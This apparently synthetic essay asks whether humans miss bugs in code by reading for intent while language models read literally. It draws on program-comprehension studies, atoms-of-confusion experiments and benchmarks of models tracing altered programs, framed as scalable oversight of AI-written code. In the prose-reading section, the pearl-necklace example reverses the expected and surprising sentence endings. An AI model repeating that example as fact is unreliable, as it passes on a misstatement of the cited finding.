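# Literal and intended reading of code in the oversight of AI-written software

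## What a program does and what it was meant to do

In code review, one or more developers inspect a colleague's proposed change to a program before it joins the codebase, the team's shared source code. *Trust-Calibrated Code Review* (2026) describes the modern form of this practice as informal, lightweight and asynchronous. The change normally arrives as a pull request, a set of edits with a short description, which reviewers can discuss, send back or merge. Teams use review to catch bugs, but also to pass on knowledge and to keep a say in what goes into their product.

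Language models now both write and review code. *Do People Prefer "Natural" code?* (2019) defines a language model as a program that assigns probabilities to text. Large language models, trained on huge amounts of prose and source code, can write programs and comment on them. A coding agent is a language model that uses tools to open files, run commands and work through a task in many steps, often up to a finished pull request. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (Agarwal, Miller and colleagues, 2026) cites a count of over 400,000 pull requests that one agent, OpenAI's Codex, opened on the code-hosting site GitHub within two months of its release. According to *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2025), a model reviews every pull request inside OpenAI, and by October 2025 the same system was handling more than 100,000 pull requests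 a day from outside the company.

Trębacz and colleagues built that reviewer because agents produce more code than people can check thoroughly, and that code may contain severe flaws, whether accidental or deliberate. This is part of the general problem of scalable oversight, which is how to supervise AI work that is too large or too hard for people to check unaided. In a talk also titled *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale*, the speaker describes the aim for code as making people's ability to verify it grow as quickly as AI's ability to produce it. One candidate method is to have models check the work of models, while people read whatever they still have time to read. How much this improves safety depends on which flaws the models and the people each overlook.

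### Literal reading, intended reading and specifications

*A Theory of Dual Channel Constraints* (Casalnuovo, Barr and colleagues, 2020) describes source code as having two channels. The algorithmic channel specifies what the computer executes. The natural-language channel, mainly comments and the names programmers choose for functions and variables, explains the code's purpose to other people, and the computer ignores it. Literal reading means working out what a program does from its instructions alone. Intended reading means working out what its author meant it to do, using names, comments, context and convention. Naming cues are the hints about purpose that names give.

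Suppose a developer has a meaning *m* in mind and writes the program text *l*. Once the compiler and platform are fixed, *l* has a single interpretation for a machine, with probability 1. According to Casalnuovo and colleagues, a human reader avoids computing that interpretation where possible and instead guesses what the author meant. The guess is a probability distribution *p*(*m′* | *l*) over the meanings *m′* that the author might have had. Good names and familiar constructions raise the probability of the right meaning, and eccentric ones lower it. Because familiar constructions are part of the instructions, the machine and human readings do not correspond neatly to code and comments. An experienced programmer can guess what a loop is for from its shape, without help from names.

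A specification is a statement, formal or informal, of what a program should do. The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *The Philosophy of Computer Science* follows the philosopher Raymond Turner, who holds that a text becomes a specification once it has "correctness jurisdiction" over the thing built. If the program and the specification disagree, the program contains a bug and has to change.

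Turner concedes that this is an idealisation, because specifications can misstate what people wanted. The encyclopedia's example is a phone app that filters out calls from call centres. Its specification is to keep a blacklist of numbers and update it every so many days. A program could follow that exactly and still let through a call centre that changed its number yesterday. The broader definition of a bug is therefore more useful here: a mismatch between what a program does and what someone meant it to do. The specification is the best available record of what they meant.

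### One function under two names

Here is a short function in the language Python. It takes a list of invoices and returns True or False.

```python
def all_paid(invoices):
    for invoice in invoices:
        if invoice.paid:
            return True
    return False
```

If the function is given two invoices, the first paid and the second unpaid, it returns True as soon as the loop reaches the first, without checking the second. By its name, it should return False, since one invoice is unpaid. A correct version would return False at the first unpaid invoice, and True only after the loop has run to the end.

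Now rename the function `any_paid` and change nothing else. The trace is identical, line for line, and the code is correct.

| Invoices | The function returns | Correct for `all_paid` | Correct for `any_paid` |
|---|---|---|---|
| paid, paid | True | True | True |
| unpaid, unpaid | False | False | False |
| paid, unpaid | True | False | True |
| empty list | False | True, by Python's convention | False |

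A tester who tries only a list where every invoice is paid and a list where none is will find no error under either name. But ten invoices can be paid or unpaid in 1,024 ways, and `all_paid` gives the wrong answer for all 1,022 that mix paid and unpaid invoices.

The example also shows that literal reading alone cannot find every bug. A reader who attended only to the instructions could describe this function perfectly and have no reason to object to it. Some faults can be recognized with very little knowledge of intent, because hardly anyone wants a program to crash or leak passwords. To find the others, a reader has to consider both what the code does and what it was meant to do, and keep the two separate.

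### Recovering the behaviour, recovering the intent, comparing them

Bug detection has three steps. The reader works out what the code does (for example, a function returns True if at least one invoice is paid), works out what it was meant to do (return True only if every invoice is paid), and compares the two.

A reader working out what a program does can simply miscalculate, but the subtler and more important failure here is to infer the behaviour from the apparent intent. Someone sees the name `all_paid`, a loop over invoices, a test of whether each is paid, a True and a False, and concludes that the function checks every invoice. Casalnuovo and colleagues explain that this shortcut is appealing because executing code in one's head takes a lot of effort, and reading the name of a function correctly called `quicksort` is far easier than stepping through the sorting algorithm. Names in decently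 written software are mostly right, so the shortcut usually works.

Models can also make mistakes at this step. In *Can chatbots craft correct code?*, published by the security firm Trail of Bits, one of the firm's engineers asked Claude Opus 4.5, Gemini 3 Pro and ChatGPT 5.2 to translate into Python a C function that adds one to an integer. All three wrote Python that looks the same as the C. But when the integer is already the largest its type can hold, C leaves the result undefined (the value might wrap round, or the program might crash), whereas Python returns a bigger number. None of the models pointed this out. It is hard to say whether they misread the C or judged the difference too small to mention, and the original developer may have known that the inputs never get that large.

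Intent is harder to recover when the code gives fewer clues than `all_paid` does. O'Reilly's *AI Code Review Only Catches Half of Your Bugs* describes an app that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, built to say when to leave home for a bus. The agent picked the wrong stop, so the app accurately predicted the wait for a bus going the opposite way. Nothing in the code looked wrong. A reviewer without requirements can see what code does but not what it should do, a limit the article calls the "intent ceiling". The article estimates that about half of all security defects lie above that ceiling. That estimate rests largely on a 2006 book, and the article's author is promoting a tool for writing requirements, so the figure deserves less trust than the explanation of why reviewers miss such defects.

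Without a statement of intent, a reader may also assume that the code does what it was meant to do. If the invoice function had been called `check`, a careful reader would work out that it returns True at the first paid invoice and might well assume that this was its job. Similarly, in O'Reilly's other example, Gson, a widely used Google library for reading data files, silently accepted duplicate keys whenever the first value was null. The fault survived years of tests and reviews. O'Reilly's tool found it after deriving a requirement from users' old complaints on GitHub, some from 2016, and Gson's maintainers merged the fix.

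Readers can also infer the wrong intent. The Trail of Bits engineer had written a plagiarism detector containing a recursive function, one that calls itself. Recursion in Python can exhaust memory if it goes too deep, and when a user's run crashed, Claude blamed the function and rewrote it. The rewrite stopped the crash, but the program no longer produced its output. The recursion had been safe because its inputs never took it more than a few levels deep. The crash was caused by two files whose names differed only in capitalization.

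When a model wrote the code, there may be no settled intent to recover. Reviewers normally ask a colleague why a change looks as it does, but a model's answer to that question may be a confabulation, as *Trust-Calibrated Code Review* points out. *Guiding Human Validation of LLM-Generated Code via Verifiable Literate Programming* (2026) examined bugs in code from two models and found that a person could spot most of them from a plain-language description of the code's behaviour (156 of 191 for DeepSeek and 169 of 203 for Claude Opus). The largest group of these spottable bugs, 44% to 47%, arose because the prompt left something open and the model made a plausible assumption that no user had confirmed.

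A reader may understand what the code does and still go wrong in the comparison, by measuring it against a requirement that nobody made. The empty list in the table is a small example, because a reader cannot tell from the name `all_paid` what a shop with no invoices wants to see. *What Do Explanations and Fixes Add to LLM Code Review?* (2026) cites a 2024 finding by Tong and Zhang that a model judged code too strictly because it demanded unnecessary error handling. It also reports results from RTLReview-Bench, in which twelve current models judged matched pairs of correct and buggy modules in Verilog, a language for describing hardware. All but one missed at most 3.5% of the buggy modules, but the models rejected between 2% and 59% of the correct ones. Those rates do not show which step went wrong. They do show that a reviewer can have a low miss rate (the share of real bugs it fails to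 report) because it is ready to object to everything, which does not necessarily mean it has read the code literally.

Another way to find bugs is to look for improbable code, which doesn't require tracing the program's steps. *On the "Naturalness" of Buggy Code* (2015) found that language models assign markedly lower probability to buggy code than to other code, and that inspecting the improbable parts worked about as well as two conventional bug-finding tools. Names can help make a line improbable. *LineBreaker* (2024) describes a Python function containing the line `path_quoted = quote(path)` and, just below it, `params_quoted = quote(query)`. The second line should plainly quote `params`, and one can see that without knowing what `quote` does. Similarly, `return True` is unusual inside the loop of a function called `all_paid`, so a model might flag it without tracing how the loop handles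 any invoice.

### The hypothesis and its predictions

The hypothesis under test is that people miss bugs because they read code for what it was meant to do, while language models catch them because they read it for what it actually does. This leads to three predictions.

People's errors should depend on the names in the code. Suppose a function called `all_paid` returns True for one paid and one unpaid invoice. People who get its output wrong should say False, and they should stop making this mistake when the function is renamed `any_paid`. A model should answer True under either name, and any errors it makes should come from the code's length or complexity. People and models should also miss different bugs, so their error correlation, the degree to which two reviewers miss the same bugs, should be low.

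Nobody appears to have tested all of this together, and it is hard to find anyone who has stated it in full. The closest is a reader's comment on the Linux news site LWN.net, *AI review?* (iabervon, 2025), which suggests that a long-overlooked bug survives because "you've been reading the code as if it was the predictable, correct thing", whereas a language model will do well at pointing to the most statistically unlikely text. This account of human readers matches the hypothesis, but the hypothesis attributes the model's advantage to literal reading rather than to noticing surprising text. iabervon adds that the method does not help with a correct patch, or with a bug that looks just as everyone expects. Casalnuovo and colleagues supply a theory of why people read code this way, but they do not claim that models read differently. If anything, their theory gives reason to expect that models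 read similarly, because programmers choose names and code structures together, in conventional combinations, and a model trained on the resulting code has every opportunity to learn that names predict behaviour.

*LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs* (2024) found that OpenAI's model critics caught many more deliberately inserted bugs than paid human reviewers did. It attributes most of the gap to the people writing shorter reviews, lacking domain knowledge and facing hard tasks, in that order, and doesn't mention reading for intent as a cause. Claude Opus 4.6 has found serious vulnerabilities that had gone unnoticed for decades, and a passage in Schneier on Security's *LLMs are Getting a Lot Better and Faster at Finding and Exploiting Zero-Days* (2026) describes it as reasoning about code "the way a human researcher would". Two of the three methods the passage lists, looking for bugs similar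 to past ones and spotting patterns that tend to cause trouble, are forms of recognition. *How Accurately Do Large Language Models Understand Code?* (Haroon, Khan and colleagues, 2025) found that older models could no longer locate 78% of the bugs they had found once the code was edited in ways that didn't change its behaviour, though misleading variable names had the least effect.

The predictions can also fail. People and models might miss different bugs because they know different things, not because of the names in the code. If nobody wrote down what the program was meant to do, both might miss the same bugs even if they read the code differently.

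Misleading renaming replaces a program's names with ones that suggest a different purpose but leaves its behaviour unchanged, to see whether reviewers change their verdict. If the name is the only evidence of intent, they should change it. The invoice function, for example, is wrong as `all_paid` and right as `any_paid`. A fair test must therefore either state the specification separately, so that it stays fixed while the names vary, or use execution prediction, in which the reader gives the output for a particular input without running the program. For one paid and one unpaid invoice, that output is True whatever the function is called.

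## Why people read past errors in code

*Program Comprehension During Software Maintenance and Evolution* (von Mayrhauser and Vans, 1995) compares six theories of how programmers understand code. In all six, the reader forms hypotheses about the code and then confirms, revises or drops them. The prediction that people's errors follow the names in the code is consistent with these theories, because a reader who works from hypotheses can settle on a wrong one. But people can also misread code for reasons unrelated to its apparent purpose.

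### Guessing first and checking afterwards

Ruven Brooks's 1983 theory goes furthest, since it holds that hypotheses alone drive understanding. As von Mayrhauser and Vans describe it, the reader starts with a primary hypothesis, a broad, rather vague idea of what the program does, and breaks it into narrower hypotheses until each one matches particular lines of code or a passage in a document. To find the matches, the reader looks for beacons, familiar fragments that hint at a purpose. Swapping two values inside a loop is a beacon for sorting, and so is a procedure named `Sort`. The reader has finished when every hypothesis has something to support it.

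The invoice function `all_paid` wrongly returns True at the first paid invoice. Its name suggests the primary hypothesis, that it checks whether every invoice is paid, and the loop, the test and the two possible answers all seem to confirm this. In Brooks's theory, a hypothesis fails if the reader can't find code to support it, if one piece of code supports rival hypotheses, or if some code has no explanation. Nothing is missing from `all_paid`, and no line looks out of place. The loop also supports a rival hypothesis, that the function looks for any paid invoice, but only a reader who has thought of that alternative will notice.

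The theory therefore predicts that people will usually notice a missing loop but will often read past a bug in code that has the expected parts in the wrong arrangement.

Other theories have the reader work in the opposite direction. In Ben Shneiderman and Richard Mayer's theory, the reader starts with the lines of code, groups them into chunks and works up to the problem that the program solves. This more literal-sounding process also discards detail, because the reader replaces each chunk with a label once they recognize it. Someone who has labelled the loop "checks that every invoice is paid" will then reason from the label, and won't look at the loop again unless something prompts them to.

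How closely people read code depends on what they already know. Von Mayrhauser and Vans distinguish shallow reasoning, which matches a familiar pattern to the code without analysing it, from deep reasoning, which works out how the parts affect one another. Many experts reason shallowly when they recognize a pattern, so experience might make some bugs easier to miss. But experts also give up doubtful hypotheses much faster than novices do. Most of the theories describe someone trying to understand a whole program rather than find a bug, and a suspicious reviewer may well read more closely than they predict.

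Guessing is harder to avoid in large programs. The code that serves one purpose may be spread across several distant places, and a programmer in a hurry may look at only one of them. Letovsky and Soloway (1986), in *Delocalized Plans and Program Comprehension*, found that programmers then infer the purpose from names and other local clues. This often works, but it can lead to false assumptions.

### Code that breaks convention

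If programmers read by matching patterns, they should make more mistakes with unconventional code. Elliot Soloway, Kate Ehrlich and their colleagues at Yale tested this in the early 1980s. In *Empirical Studies of Programming Knowledge*, Soloway and Ehrlich propose that experts know plans, which are standard fragments for routine jobs such as keeping a running total, and rules of discourse, which are conventions for combining plans. One rule is that a programmer doesn't test for something that can't happen.

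Soloway, Ehrlich and Gold (1983), in *Reading A Program Is Like Reading A Story (Well, Almost)*, gave students a short program with one line missing and asked for the line that most reasonably completed it. The students had reached at least the end of their second semester of programming, and nobody told them what the program was for. It averages the numbers that a user types in, and stops at 99999, an end marker that should not affect the result. Half the students saw a conventional version, in which a check keeps the end marker out of the sum. The other half saw a version that would look roughly like this in Python:

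```python
total = -99999
# missing line
while True:
    number = read_number()
    total = total + number
    count = count + 1
    if number == 99999:
        break
average = total / count
```

This program adds the end marker to the total and counts it as one of the numbers. To compensate, the total starts at −99999, and the missing line must set the count to −1. If the user types 4, 6 and 99999, the total comes to 10, the count to 2 and the average to 5. If the count started at the usual 0, it would reach 3 and the average would be 3.33.

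Of the 47 students who had the conventional version, 37 supplied the right line, compared with only 3 of the 44 who had the unconventional version. The unconventional program is shorter and scores as simpler on standard measures of complexity, so length can't explain the difference. The three students who succeeded on the unconventional version took almost four minutes on average. The 41 who failed took 2.42 minutes, barely longer than the 2.26 minutes taken by students who completed the conventional version correctly. Most of the 41 apparently saw nothing that called for a closer reading, even though the program contained the strange starting value of −99999.

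This is good evidence that convention can override the instructions on the page, but weaker evidence about code review. The participants were students, three people are too few for a reliable average, and asking for the most "reasonable" line tends to encourage a conventional answer. Both versions also used the same variable names, so the experiment shows the effect of familiar structure, not of naming cues.

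An earlier experiment, reported in *Tacit Programming Knowledge* (Soloway and Ehrlich, 1982), shows how one line of code can change what people expect of another. It used a program that prints ten square roots, with the line that sets the number N left blank. Just before taking the root, the program checks whether N is negative and, if so, reverses its sign. Experienced readers assume the check is there because N could be negative, so they infer that N probably comes from the user rather than from a simple formula. In a second version, the program also sets N to 0 before the loop, which by convention suggests that the program will calculate N itself.

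When these two clues conflicted, novices were significantly less likely to favour having the user supply N. More advanced programmers still preferred it, but they took significantly longer than the novices, although they had been faster on the version without a conflict. This fits the theory that people read quickly until they notice something unexpected. It also shows that experienced readers infer what code does from the mere presence of a line. The same habit could wrongly reassure a reviewer if a programmer adds a safety check by mistake or the check tests the wrong thing.

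Expectation usually helps people read code correctly, however. *How do Humans and LLMs Process Confusing Code?* (Abdelsalam, Peitek and colleagues, 2025) cites an experiment by Casalnuovo's group in which programmers answered questions about snippets that did the same thing in more and less predictable ways. The programmers were slower and less accurate on the less predictable versions. A team that wrote strange code to keep its reviewers alert would probably end up with more misreadings.

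### Atoms of confusion

People also misread code that gives no hint of its purpose. *Atoms of Confusion* (Gopstein, 2017) defines confusion as a programmer's belief that code will behave differently from how it does. An atom of confusion is the smallest piece of code that often causes this. In *Understanding misunderstandings in source code*, Gopstein, Iannacone and colleagues (2017) looked for such atoms using execution prediction, showing people tiny C programs and asking what each would print.

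The team collected 19 potentially confusing patterns from winners of the International Obfuscated C Code Contest, whose entrants compete to write unreadable programs. They then wrote 126 short programs as matched pairs. One program in each pair contained one of the patterns, and the other did the same thing more plainly. Each of 73 participants predicted the output of 84 programs. For 15 of the 19 patterns, participants made significantly more mistakes on the programs containing the pattern than on the plainer versions.

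In a talk on the results, Gopstein, Iannacone and colleagues gave an effect size for every pattern, on a scale where 0.1 is small and 0.5 is large. The table shows some of these effect sizes, including one for a candidate pattern that did not confuse anyone.

| Pattern | Example | What happens | Effect size |
|---|---|---|---|
| Change of literal encoding | `printf("%d", 013)` | Prints 11, because a leading zero means base 8 | 0.60 |
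| Macro operator precedence | `M1 * 2`, where `M1` stands for `64 - 1` | Gives 62, because C pastes in the text and multiplies first | 0.36 |
| Post-increment | `V1 = V2++` | `V1` gets the old value of `V2`, which then goes up by one | 0.34 |
| Implicit predicate | `if (4 % 2)` | The condition is false, because the remainder is 0 | 0.10 |
| Constant variable | `int V1 = 5; printf("%d", V1);` | Prints 5 | 0.00 |

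The share of correct answers was 60 percentage points lower for the pattern at the top of the table than for the plain version, and 10 points lower for the implicit predicate, the weakest of the 15 confirmed patterns.

A second experiment used four larger programs, all contest winners. The researchers tidied the layout, removed hints about meaning, and made one version of each program with the atoms and one without. None of the 43 participants saw both versions of the same program. Without the atoms, participants were five times as likely to predict the entire output correctly and gave up a quarter as often.

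The effect extends beyond C. *Atoms of Confusion in Java* (Langhout and Aniche, 2021) tested 14 patterns on 132 computer science students and found that seven of the patterns made mistakes between 2.7 and 56 times as likely. The patterns also occur outside contests. *Prevalence of Confusing Code in Software Projects* (2018) counted the 15 confirmed patterns in 14 large C and C++ projects and found an average of one every 23 lines. The patterns were strongly correlated with bug fixes, though this correlation can't show that misreading caused any of the bugs.

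These results are weak evidence that people see what they expect instead of what is there. According to *Existence Experiment*, the project's description of its method, the researchers named every variable V1, V2 and so on so that only the pattern would cause confusion. The participants had no purpose to infer and knew that their job was to work out the output, so they were attempting a literal reading when they made their errors.

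To find out why, Gopstein, Fayard and colleagues (2020) later had 14 programmers talk through eight snippets each while predicting the output, in *Thinking Aloud about Confusing Code*. The programmers made 17 errors, all on snippets the original team had designed to be confusing. The researchers gave each error a main cause. In eight cases the person had never met the construct, in four they knew it but had its rules wrong, and in two they borrowed a rule from another language. One student, for example, decided that `013` must be thirteen because the computer had no need to store the zero. Only three errors were mainly lapses of attention, such as reading an assignment (`=`) as a test for equality (`==`).

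So at least 14 of the 17 errors came mainly from not knowing the language well enough. Someone who doesn't know that a leading zero means base 8 will misread `013` however carefully they look at it and whatever the surrounding names suggest. Expectation may still have contributed to some errors, such as confusing `=` with `==`, but the researchers admit that they used some guesswork when attributing errors to attention.

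The study also gives a reason not to apply the original numbers directly to professional reviewers. The five students among its 14 participants made 14 errors in 40 predictions, while the nine professionals made 3 in 72. Most of the original 73 participants were students, and they needed only three months' experience of C or C++ to take part.

Some people got the right answer for the wrong reason. One professional thought that C gives "and" and "or" equal priority and evaluates them from left to right. C actually gives "and" higher priority, but both rules lead to the same result in that snippet. Execution prediction can therefore undercount misreadings unless the test uses inputs for which the right and wrong readings give different outputs.

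### How names help people find bugs

According to the hypothesis, people miss bugs because they read for intent, but they also find bugs that way. Johnson, Draper and Soloway, who studied the mistakes in students' Pascal programs, argue that saying exactly what a bug is requires knowing what the programmer intended and understood, as well as seeing the faulty program. The invoice loop, for example, is wrong only because it doesn't do what its author intended.

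Names are usually the easiest evidence to use when working out what the author wanted. A textbook page, *Code Beacons and the Cognitive Anchors of Code Comprehension*, calls names the most common beacons. It cites a 2006 study by Lawrie and colleagues for the finding that names made of full English words work best for confirming a hypothesis. In three experiments, Crosby, Scholtz and Wiedenbeck (2002) found that experienced programmers rely on beacons while novices hardly use them, and that meaningful names make beacons more effective.

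Shen, Xi and colleagues (2026) cite research in which descriptive names also helped people find semantic defects faster, where the code is valid but does the wrong thing. The size of the benefit depended on the task and the developer's experience. This counts against the simplest version of the hypothesis, because if names mainly drew attention away from what code does, more informative names should have made these defects harder to find.

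The explanation may be that readers use a name in two ways. They learn from it what the code ought to do, and without that they have nothing to compare the behaviour with. They are also tempted to accept it as a plausible account of what the code does instead of working that out. Which effect is stronger should depend on how the bug looks. In the line `params_quoted = quote(query)`, readers can see the mistake from the names. In `all_paid`, the name fits the general shape of the loop, and readers have to follow the loop through a mixed list to discover that the name doesn't fit the behaviour.

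The miss rate also cannot be inferred from a gain in speed. In the same experiment, good names could help those who find a bug to find it sooner, while leading others to stop reading too early and miss it.

Shen and colleagues also report earlier findings that misleading beacons can give programmers a false first interpretation. For example, a procedure that shuffles a list swaps values inside a loop, as many sorting procedures do, so a reader might take it for a sort, especially if it has a name like `arrange`. Experienced programmers rely more on beacons than novices do, so they might be more prone to this mistake. But they are also quicker to drop a bad hypothesis, and the evidence doesn't show which tendency is stronger.

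A programmer who has to modify the shuffling procedure will probably find out what it does, but a reviewer with forty other files to read may never return to it and correct a mistaken first interpretation. The names in buggy code are usually not meant to deceive, however. The name `all_paid` correctly states what the programmer intended. It is dangerous because the code doesn't do what was intended, but removing the name would remove the evidence that anything is wrong.

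Reviewers also get expectations from outside the code. In Brooks's theory, documents can confirm a hypothesis just as code can, so the description on a pull request gives the reviewer a primary hypothesis before they have read a line. "Checks that all invoices are paid before closing an order" would create the same expectation as the function's name, and would still do so if somebody renamed the function. A colleague's earlier comment could also steer a reviewer, either by fixing attention on one line at the expense of the rest or by prompting a search for the same mistake elsewhere. The theory is compatible with both. The square-root experiment supports the idea that a small cue in one place changes what people expect in another, but its participants were completing a program, not reviewing a colleague's work.

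### Missing errors in prose

People also read past errors in ordinary text. When asked how many animals of each kind Moses took on the ark, many people answer "two", although they know that it was Noah. Psychologists call this a semantic illusion. Similarly, writers overlook missing words in their own work because they know what the sentence should say.

Soloway's group took their method from research on stories. As Soloway and Ehrlich recount, Bower, Black and Turner had found that people answering questions about a story fill in missing details from their knowledge of how such events normally go. People reading code use programming plans in much the same way, so someone who recognizes a running total will assume that it starts at zero.

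Brain recordings partly support the comparison. Abdelsalam and colleagues describe work by Bergum and colleagues, who recorded electrical activity from programmers' scalps while tracking their eyes. Confusing code produced a signal that peaked about 600 milliseconds after the programmer looked at it. Psychologists have found the same signal when people read sentences with an unexpected but plausible ending. For example, most people expect "he bought her a pearl necklace for her" to end with "collection", so "birthday" is mildly surprising.

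Programmers evidently form expectations about code and react when it departs from them. But this reaction occurs when something surprises the reader, and a bug that people read past doesn't surprise them. To show that expectations hide bugs, researchers would have to record people looking directly at a bug and missing it.

Reviewing code also differs from reading prose. A reader who silently corrects a typing error in a letter has still understood it, because what matters is what the writer meant. A computer runs the code as written, so a reviewer who makes the same silent correction gets a false idea of what the program will do. Many of the slips that proofreaders look for never reach a reviewer, because the compiler rejects a program that misspells a variable. The mistake in the question about the ark is a single word that the reader could have corrected from memory, but a code reviewer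 often has to calculate. Nobody remembers what a new function returns for a list of five invoices, and a bug may appear only when several correct-looking lines act together. People can miss such a bug without being under any illusion, because the calculation is long and tiring.

### How far the first prediction holds

The first prediction is that people's errors depend on the names in the code. Changing the names would test this directly. Soloway and colleagues instead kept the names and changed the structure, and the atoms experiments removed the names, so both test the prediction only indirectly.

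The broader claim that people's expectations shape how they read code is well supported. A fall from 37 correct answers out of 47 to 3 out of 44 is far too large to put down to chance, and the theories explain it well. Misleading renaming very likely affects people's answers too, since names are also beacons and misleading beacons can produce false first readings. It is much less certain how large that effect is and whether it lasts once a reviewer starts looking for bugs.

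The evidence is weakest for the idea that reading for intent explains most of what people miss. People in the atoms experiments made many mistakes on code that had no intent to read for, and this seems to be mostly because they didn't know the rules of the language. OpenAI's comparison of its critics with paid reviewers suggests that models might also outperform people by knowing more and writing fuller reviews, whether or not they read more literally.

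The distinction matters because the two problems need different remedies. Renaming the variables to V1, V2 and so on might make a reviewer trace the loop in `all_paid`, but it would not help a reviewer who thinks that `013` means thirteen. A reference manual would correct that mistake, but it would not make anyone trace the loop.

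## Whether models follow the code or its apparent purpose

Second, the hypothesis predicts that models' errors depend on the length and complexity of the code, not on the names in it. Researchers have tested this by making small edits that change what a program does, and by changing its names without affecting its behaviour. Older models do badly on both tests. Models trained to reason at length do far better, although two experiments on the same pair of recent models gave conflicting results about which one renaming affects.

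### What training teaches and what written reasoning adds

A language model learns mainly by predicting the next token, a word or part of a word, in an enormous collection of text, without running any of the code in it. The model can only learn what code does from text that reveals it, such as comments, tests, printed results and other code that calls it. In most of that text, a function called `all_paid` does check every invoice. As Shen and colleagues explain, a model that estimates the probability of an answer given the code may therefore do better by using names, even though consistent renaming wouldn't change the program's behaviour.

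When a name correctly describes what the code does, a model makes the same prediction whether it traces the loop or trusts the name, so training does little to favour tracing. To learn that names can't be trusted, a model would need to see many programs whose names and behaviour disagree, which are rare in ordinary code.

Tracing code is also hard for a model to do without writing out the steps, because it performs a limited amount of computation for each token and a loop may run hundreds of times. Written reasoning, often called chain of thought, lets the model spread the computation over many tokens. The model writes down what each variable holds after each line, then uses those notes to predict the next step. For the invoice function, it might write that the first invoice is paid, so the test succeeds and the function returns True. Reasoning models are language models that developers have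 trained further, by reinforcement learning, to write a lot of this reasoning before answering.

However, instead of tracing the code in its written steps, a model can just as easily write "this function checks that every invoice is paid" and reason from that description, as people do once they have labelled a chunk of code.

Marinov, Thimmaiah and colleagues (2026), in *Predicting Program Exit Code with LLMs and Programming Language Semantics*, show the value of written reasoning and one of its limits. They gave models the complete rules of a small programming language and asked whether each program would run or stop with an error, and which rule it would break. One variant replaced the usual operators and keywords with unfamiliar symbols. Another swapped the meanings of familiar operators, so that `+` meant subtraction and `*` meant division. The table shows the accuracy of one model, Ministral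 3 14B, on short programs written by people.

| Symbols in the program | Answer only | With written reasoning |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | 90% | 99% |
| Unfamiliar | 32% | 91% |
| Familiar, with meanings exchanged | 75% | 79% |

Writing out the steps helped models a lot when they had to look up what a strange symbol meant, but hardly at all when a familiar symbol had been given a new meaning. Accuracy fell particularly on division by zero, which in the altered language looks like a harmless multiplication, such as `3045 * 0`. One program in six contained this error, so a model that always missed it could score at most 83%, and the best models all scored around 80%. The models were small, with at most 32 billion parameters, and larger ones may follow the stated rules more faithfully.

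### Changing what the code does

Yang, Vasilakis and colleagues (2025), in *Evaluating the Generalization Capabilities of Large Language Models on Code Reasoning*, tested ten models on pairs of programs that look nearly identical but behave differently. They took a working program and made one small change, such as replacing `<` with `<=`, `and` with `or`, or 1 with 0. They kept the altered version only if it ran without an error and gave a different output for the chosen input. If several changes qualified, they picked the one that least changed which lines ran.

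Binary search, which finds a value in a sorted list by repeatedly halving the part left to search, shows how this works.

```python
def binary_search(lst, value):
    left, right = 0, len(lst) - 1
    while left < right:      # the original has <=
        mid = left + (right - left) // 2
        if lst[mid] == value:
            return mid
        elif lst[mid] < value:
            left = mid + 1
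        else:
            right = mid - 1
    return -1
```

Suppose the task is to find 5 in a list that contains only 5. The original returns 0, the position of the 5. The altered version never enters the loop, so it returns −1, meaning "not found". A model that answers 0 for the altered version has given the answer for the familiar program, an error that Yang and colleagues call reversion.

The model predicts the output of each version separately, which gives four measures:

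- **Original correctness:** the model gives the right output for the original program.
- **Original reversion:** shown the original, it gives the altered program's output.
- **Altered correctness:** it gives the right output for the altered program.
- **Altered reversion:** shown the altered program, it gives the original's output.

The reversion measures are needed because a fall in accuracy could mean only that the altered programs are harder. If a model is relying on what it already knows, it should revert much more often on the altered programs than on the originals. The reversion figures leave out programs that return True or False, because any wrong answer to those would count as a reversion. `all_paid` returns True or False, so it would be a poor test item.

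The next table gives results for well-known list functions, such as sorting and searching, that GPT-4o had written with meaningful names.

| Model | Original correct | Original reverted | Altered correct | Altered reverted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-Coder 33B (2023) | 91.7% | 2.3% | 37.3% | 54.0% |
| Qwen2.5-Coder 32B (2024) | 99.6% | 0.0% | 73.4% | 26.1% |
| GPT-4o (2024) | 100% | 0.0% | 80.1% | 16.0% |
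| DeepSeek-R1 (2025) | 100% | 0.0% | 98.2% | 0.6% |
| o3-mini (2025) | 100% | 0.0% | 99.9% | 0.0% |

Most of the older models' mistakes on altered programs were reversions. The models reverted more often on longer functions, and DeepSeek-Coder 33B did so 77% of the time on functions of around 15 lines.

Yang and colleagues also generated random list programs with no recognizable purpose and with variable names like `v1`. GPT-4o was right about 91.3% of the originals and 93.5% of the altered versions, and it almost never reverted. So the alterations caused errors when the model could revert to a familiar program, and didn't make programs harder in themselves. The familiar program needn't be one the model had seen. On solutions to programming-contest problems that appeared after its training data ended, GPT-4o's accuracy fell from 89.4% on the originals to 79.6% on the altered versions, probably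 because new solutions reuse old patterns.

Much like Soloway's students, who supplied the conventional line for an unconventional program, the older models read the code according to convention. The reasoning models (o3-mini, DeepSeek-R1 and QwQ) mostly didn't, at least on programs this short. Written reasoning alone doesn't seem to explain the difference, since Yang and colleagues had also asked the older models to reason step by step. The reasoning models may have done better because they were trained to reason at length, or simply because they are newer and better models.

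Reasoning models still recognize conventional code. In a further test, each model saw both versions of a program, with no hint that one had been altered, and worked on whichever it was more confident about. o3-mini chose the original 97% of the time for the familiar functions but only about half the time for the random programs, and it predicted the output correctly whichever it chose. This combination is promising for finding bugs, because a reviewer that can tell which code looks normal and work out what the abnormal code does has most of what it needs to compare the two.

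### Specifications for buggy code

A model has more room to report what the author probably wanted when it is asked to describe code than when it is asked to predict the output, because a prediction requires a specific answer about what the code does.

In *Specify What?*, Granberry, Ahrendt and Johansson (2024) asked GPT-4 to write formal specifications for C programs, stating what must be true of a function's inputs and what the function then guarantees about its result. Most of the programs were supposedly correct, but the researchers put mistakes resembling typos into eight of them. They generated nine specifications for each program, using three prompts, and assessed them qualitatively. The specifications reflected the programs' intended behaviour more than their actual behaviour, so the bugs had little effect.

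When GPT-4 couldn't identify a program's purpose, it tended to describe low-level details of the code. Renaming one binary search program from the uninformative `testme` to `Bsearch` noticeably improved the specification GPT-4 wrote for it. Under the old name, GPT-4 had already identified the algorithm in its written reasoning, but it specified little more than that the result would be 0 or 1.

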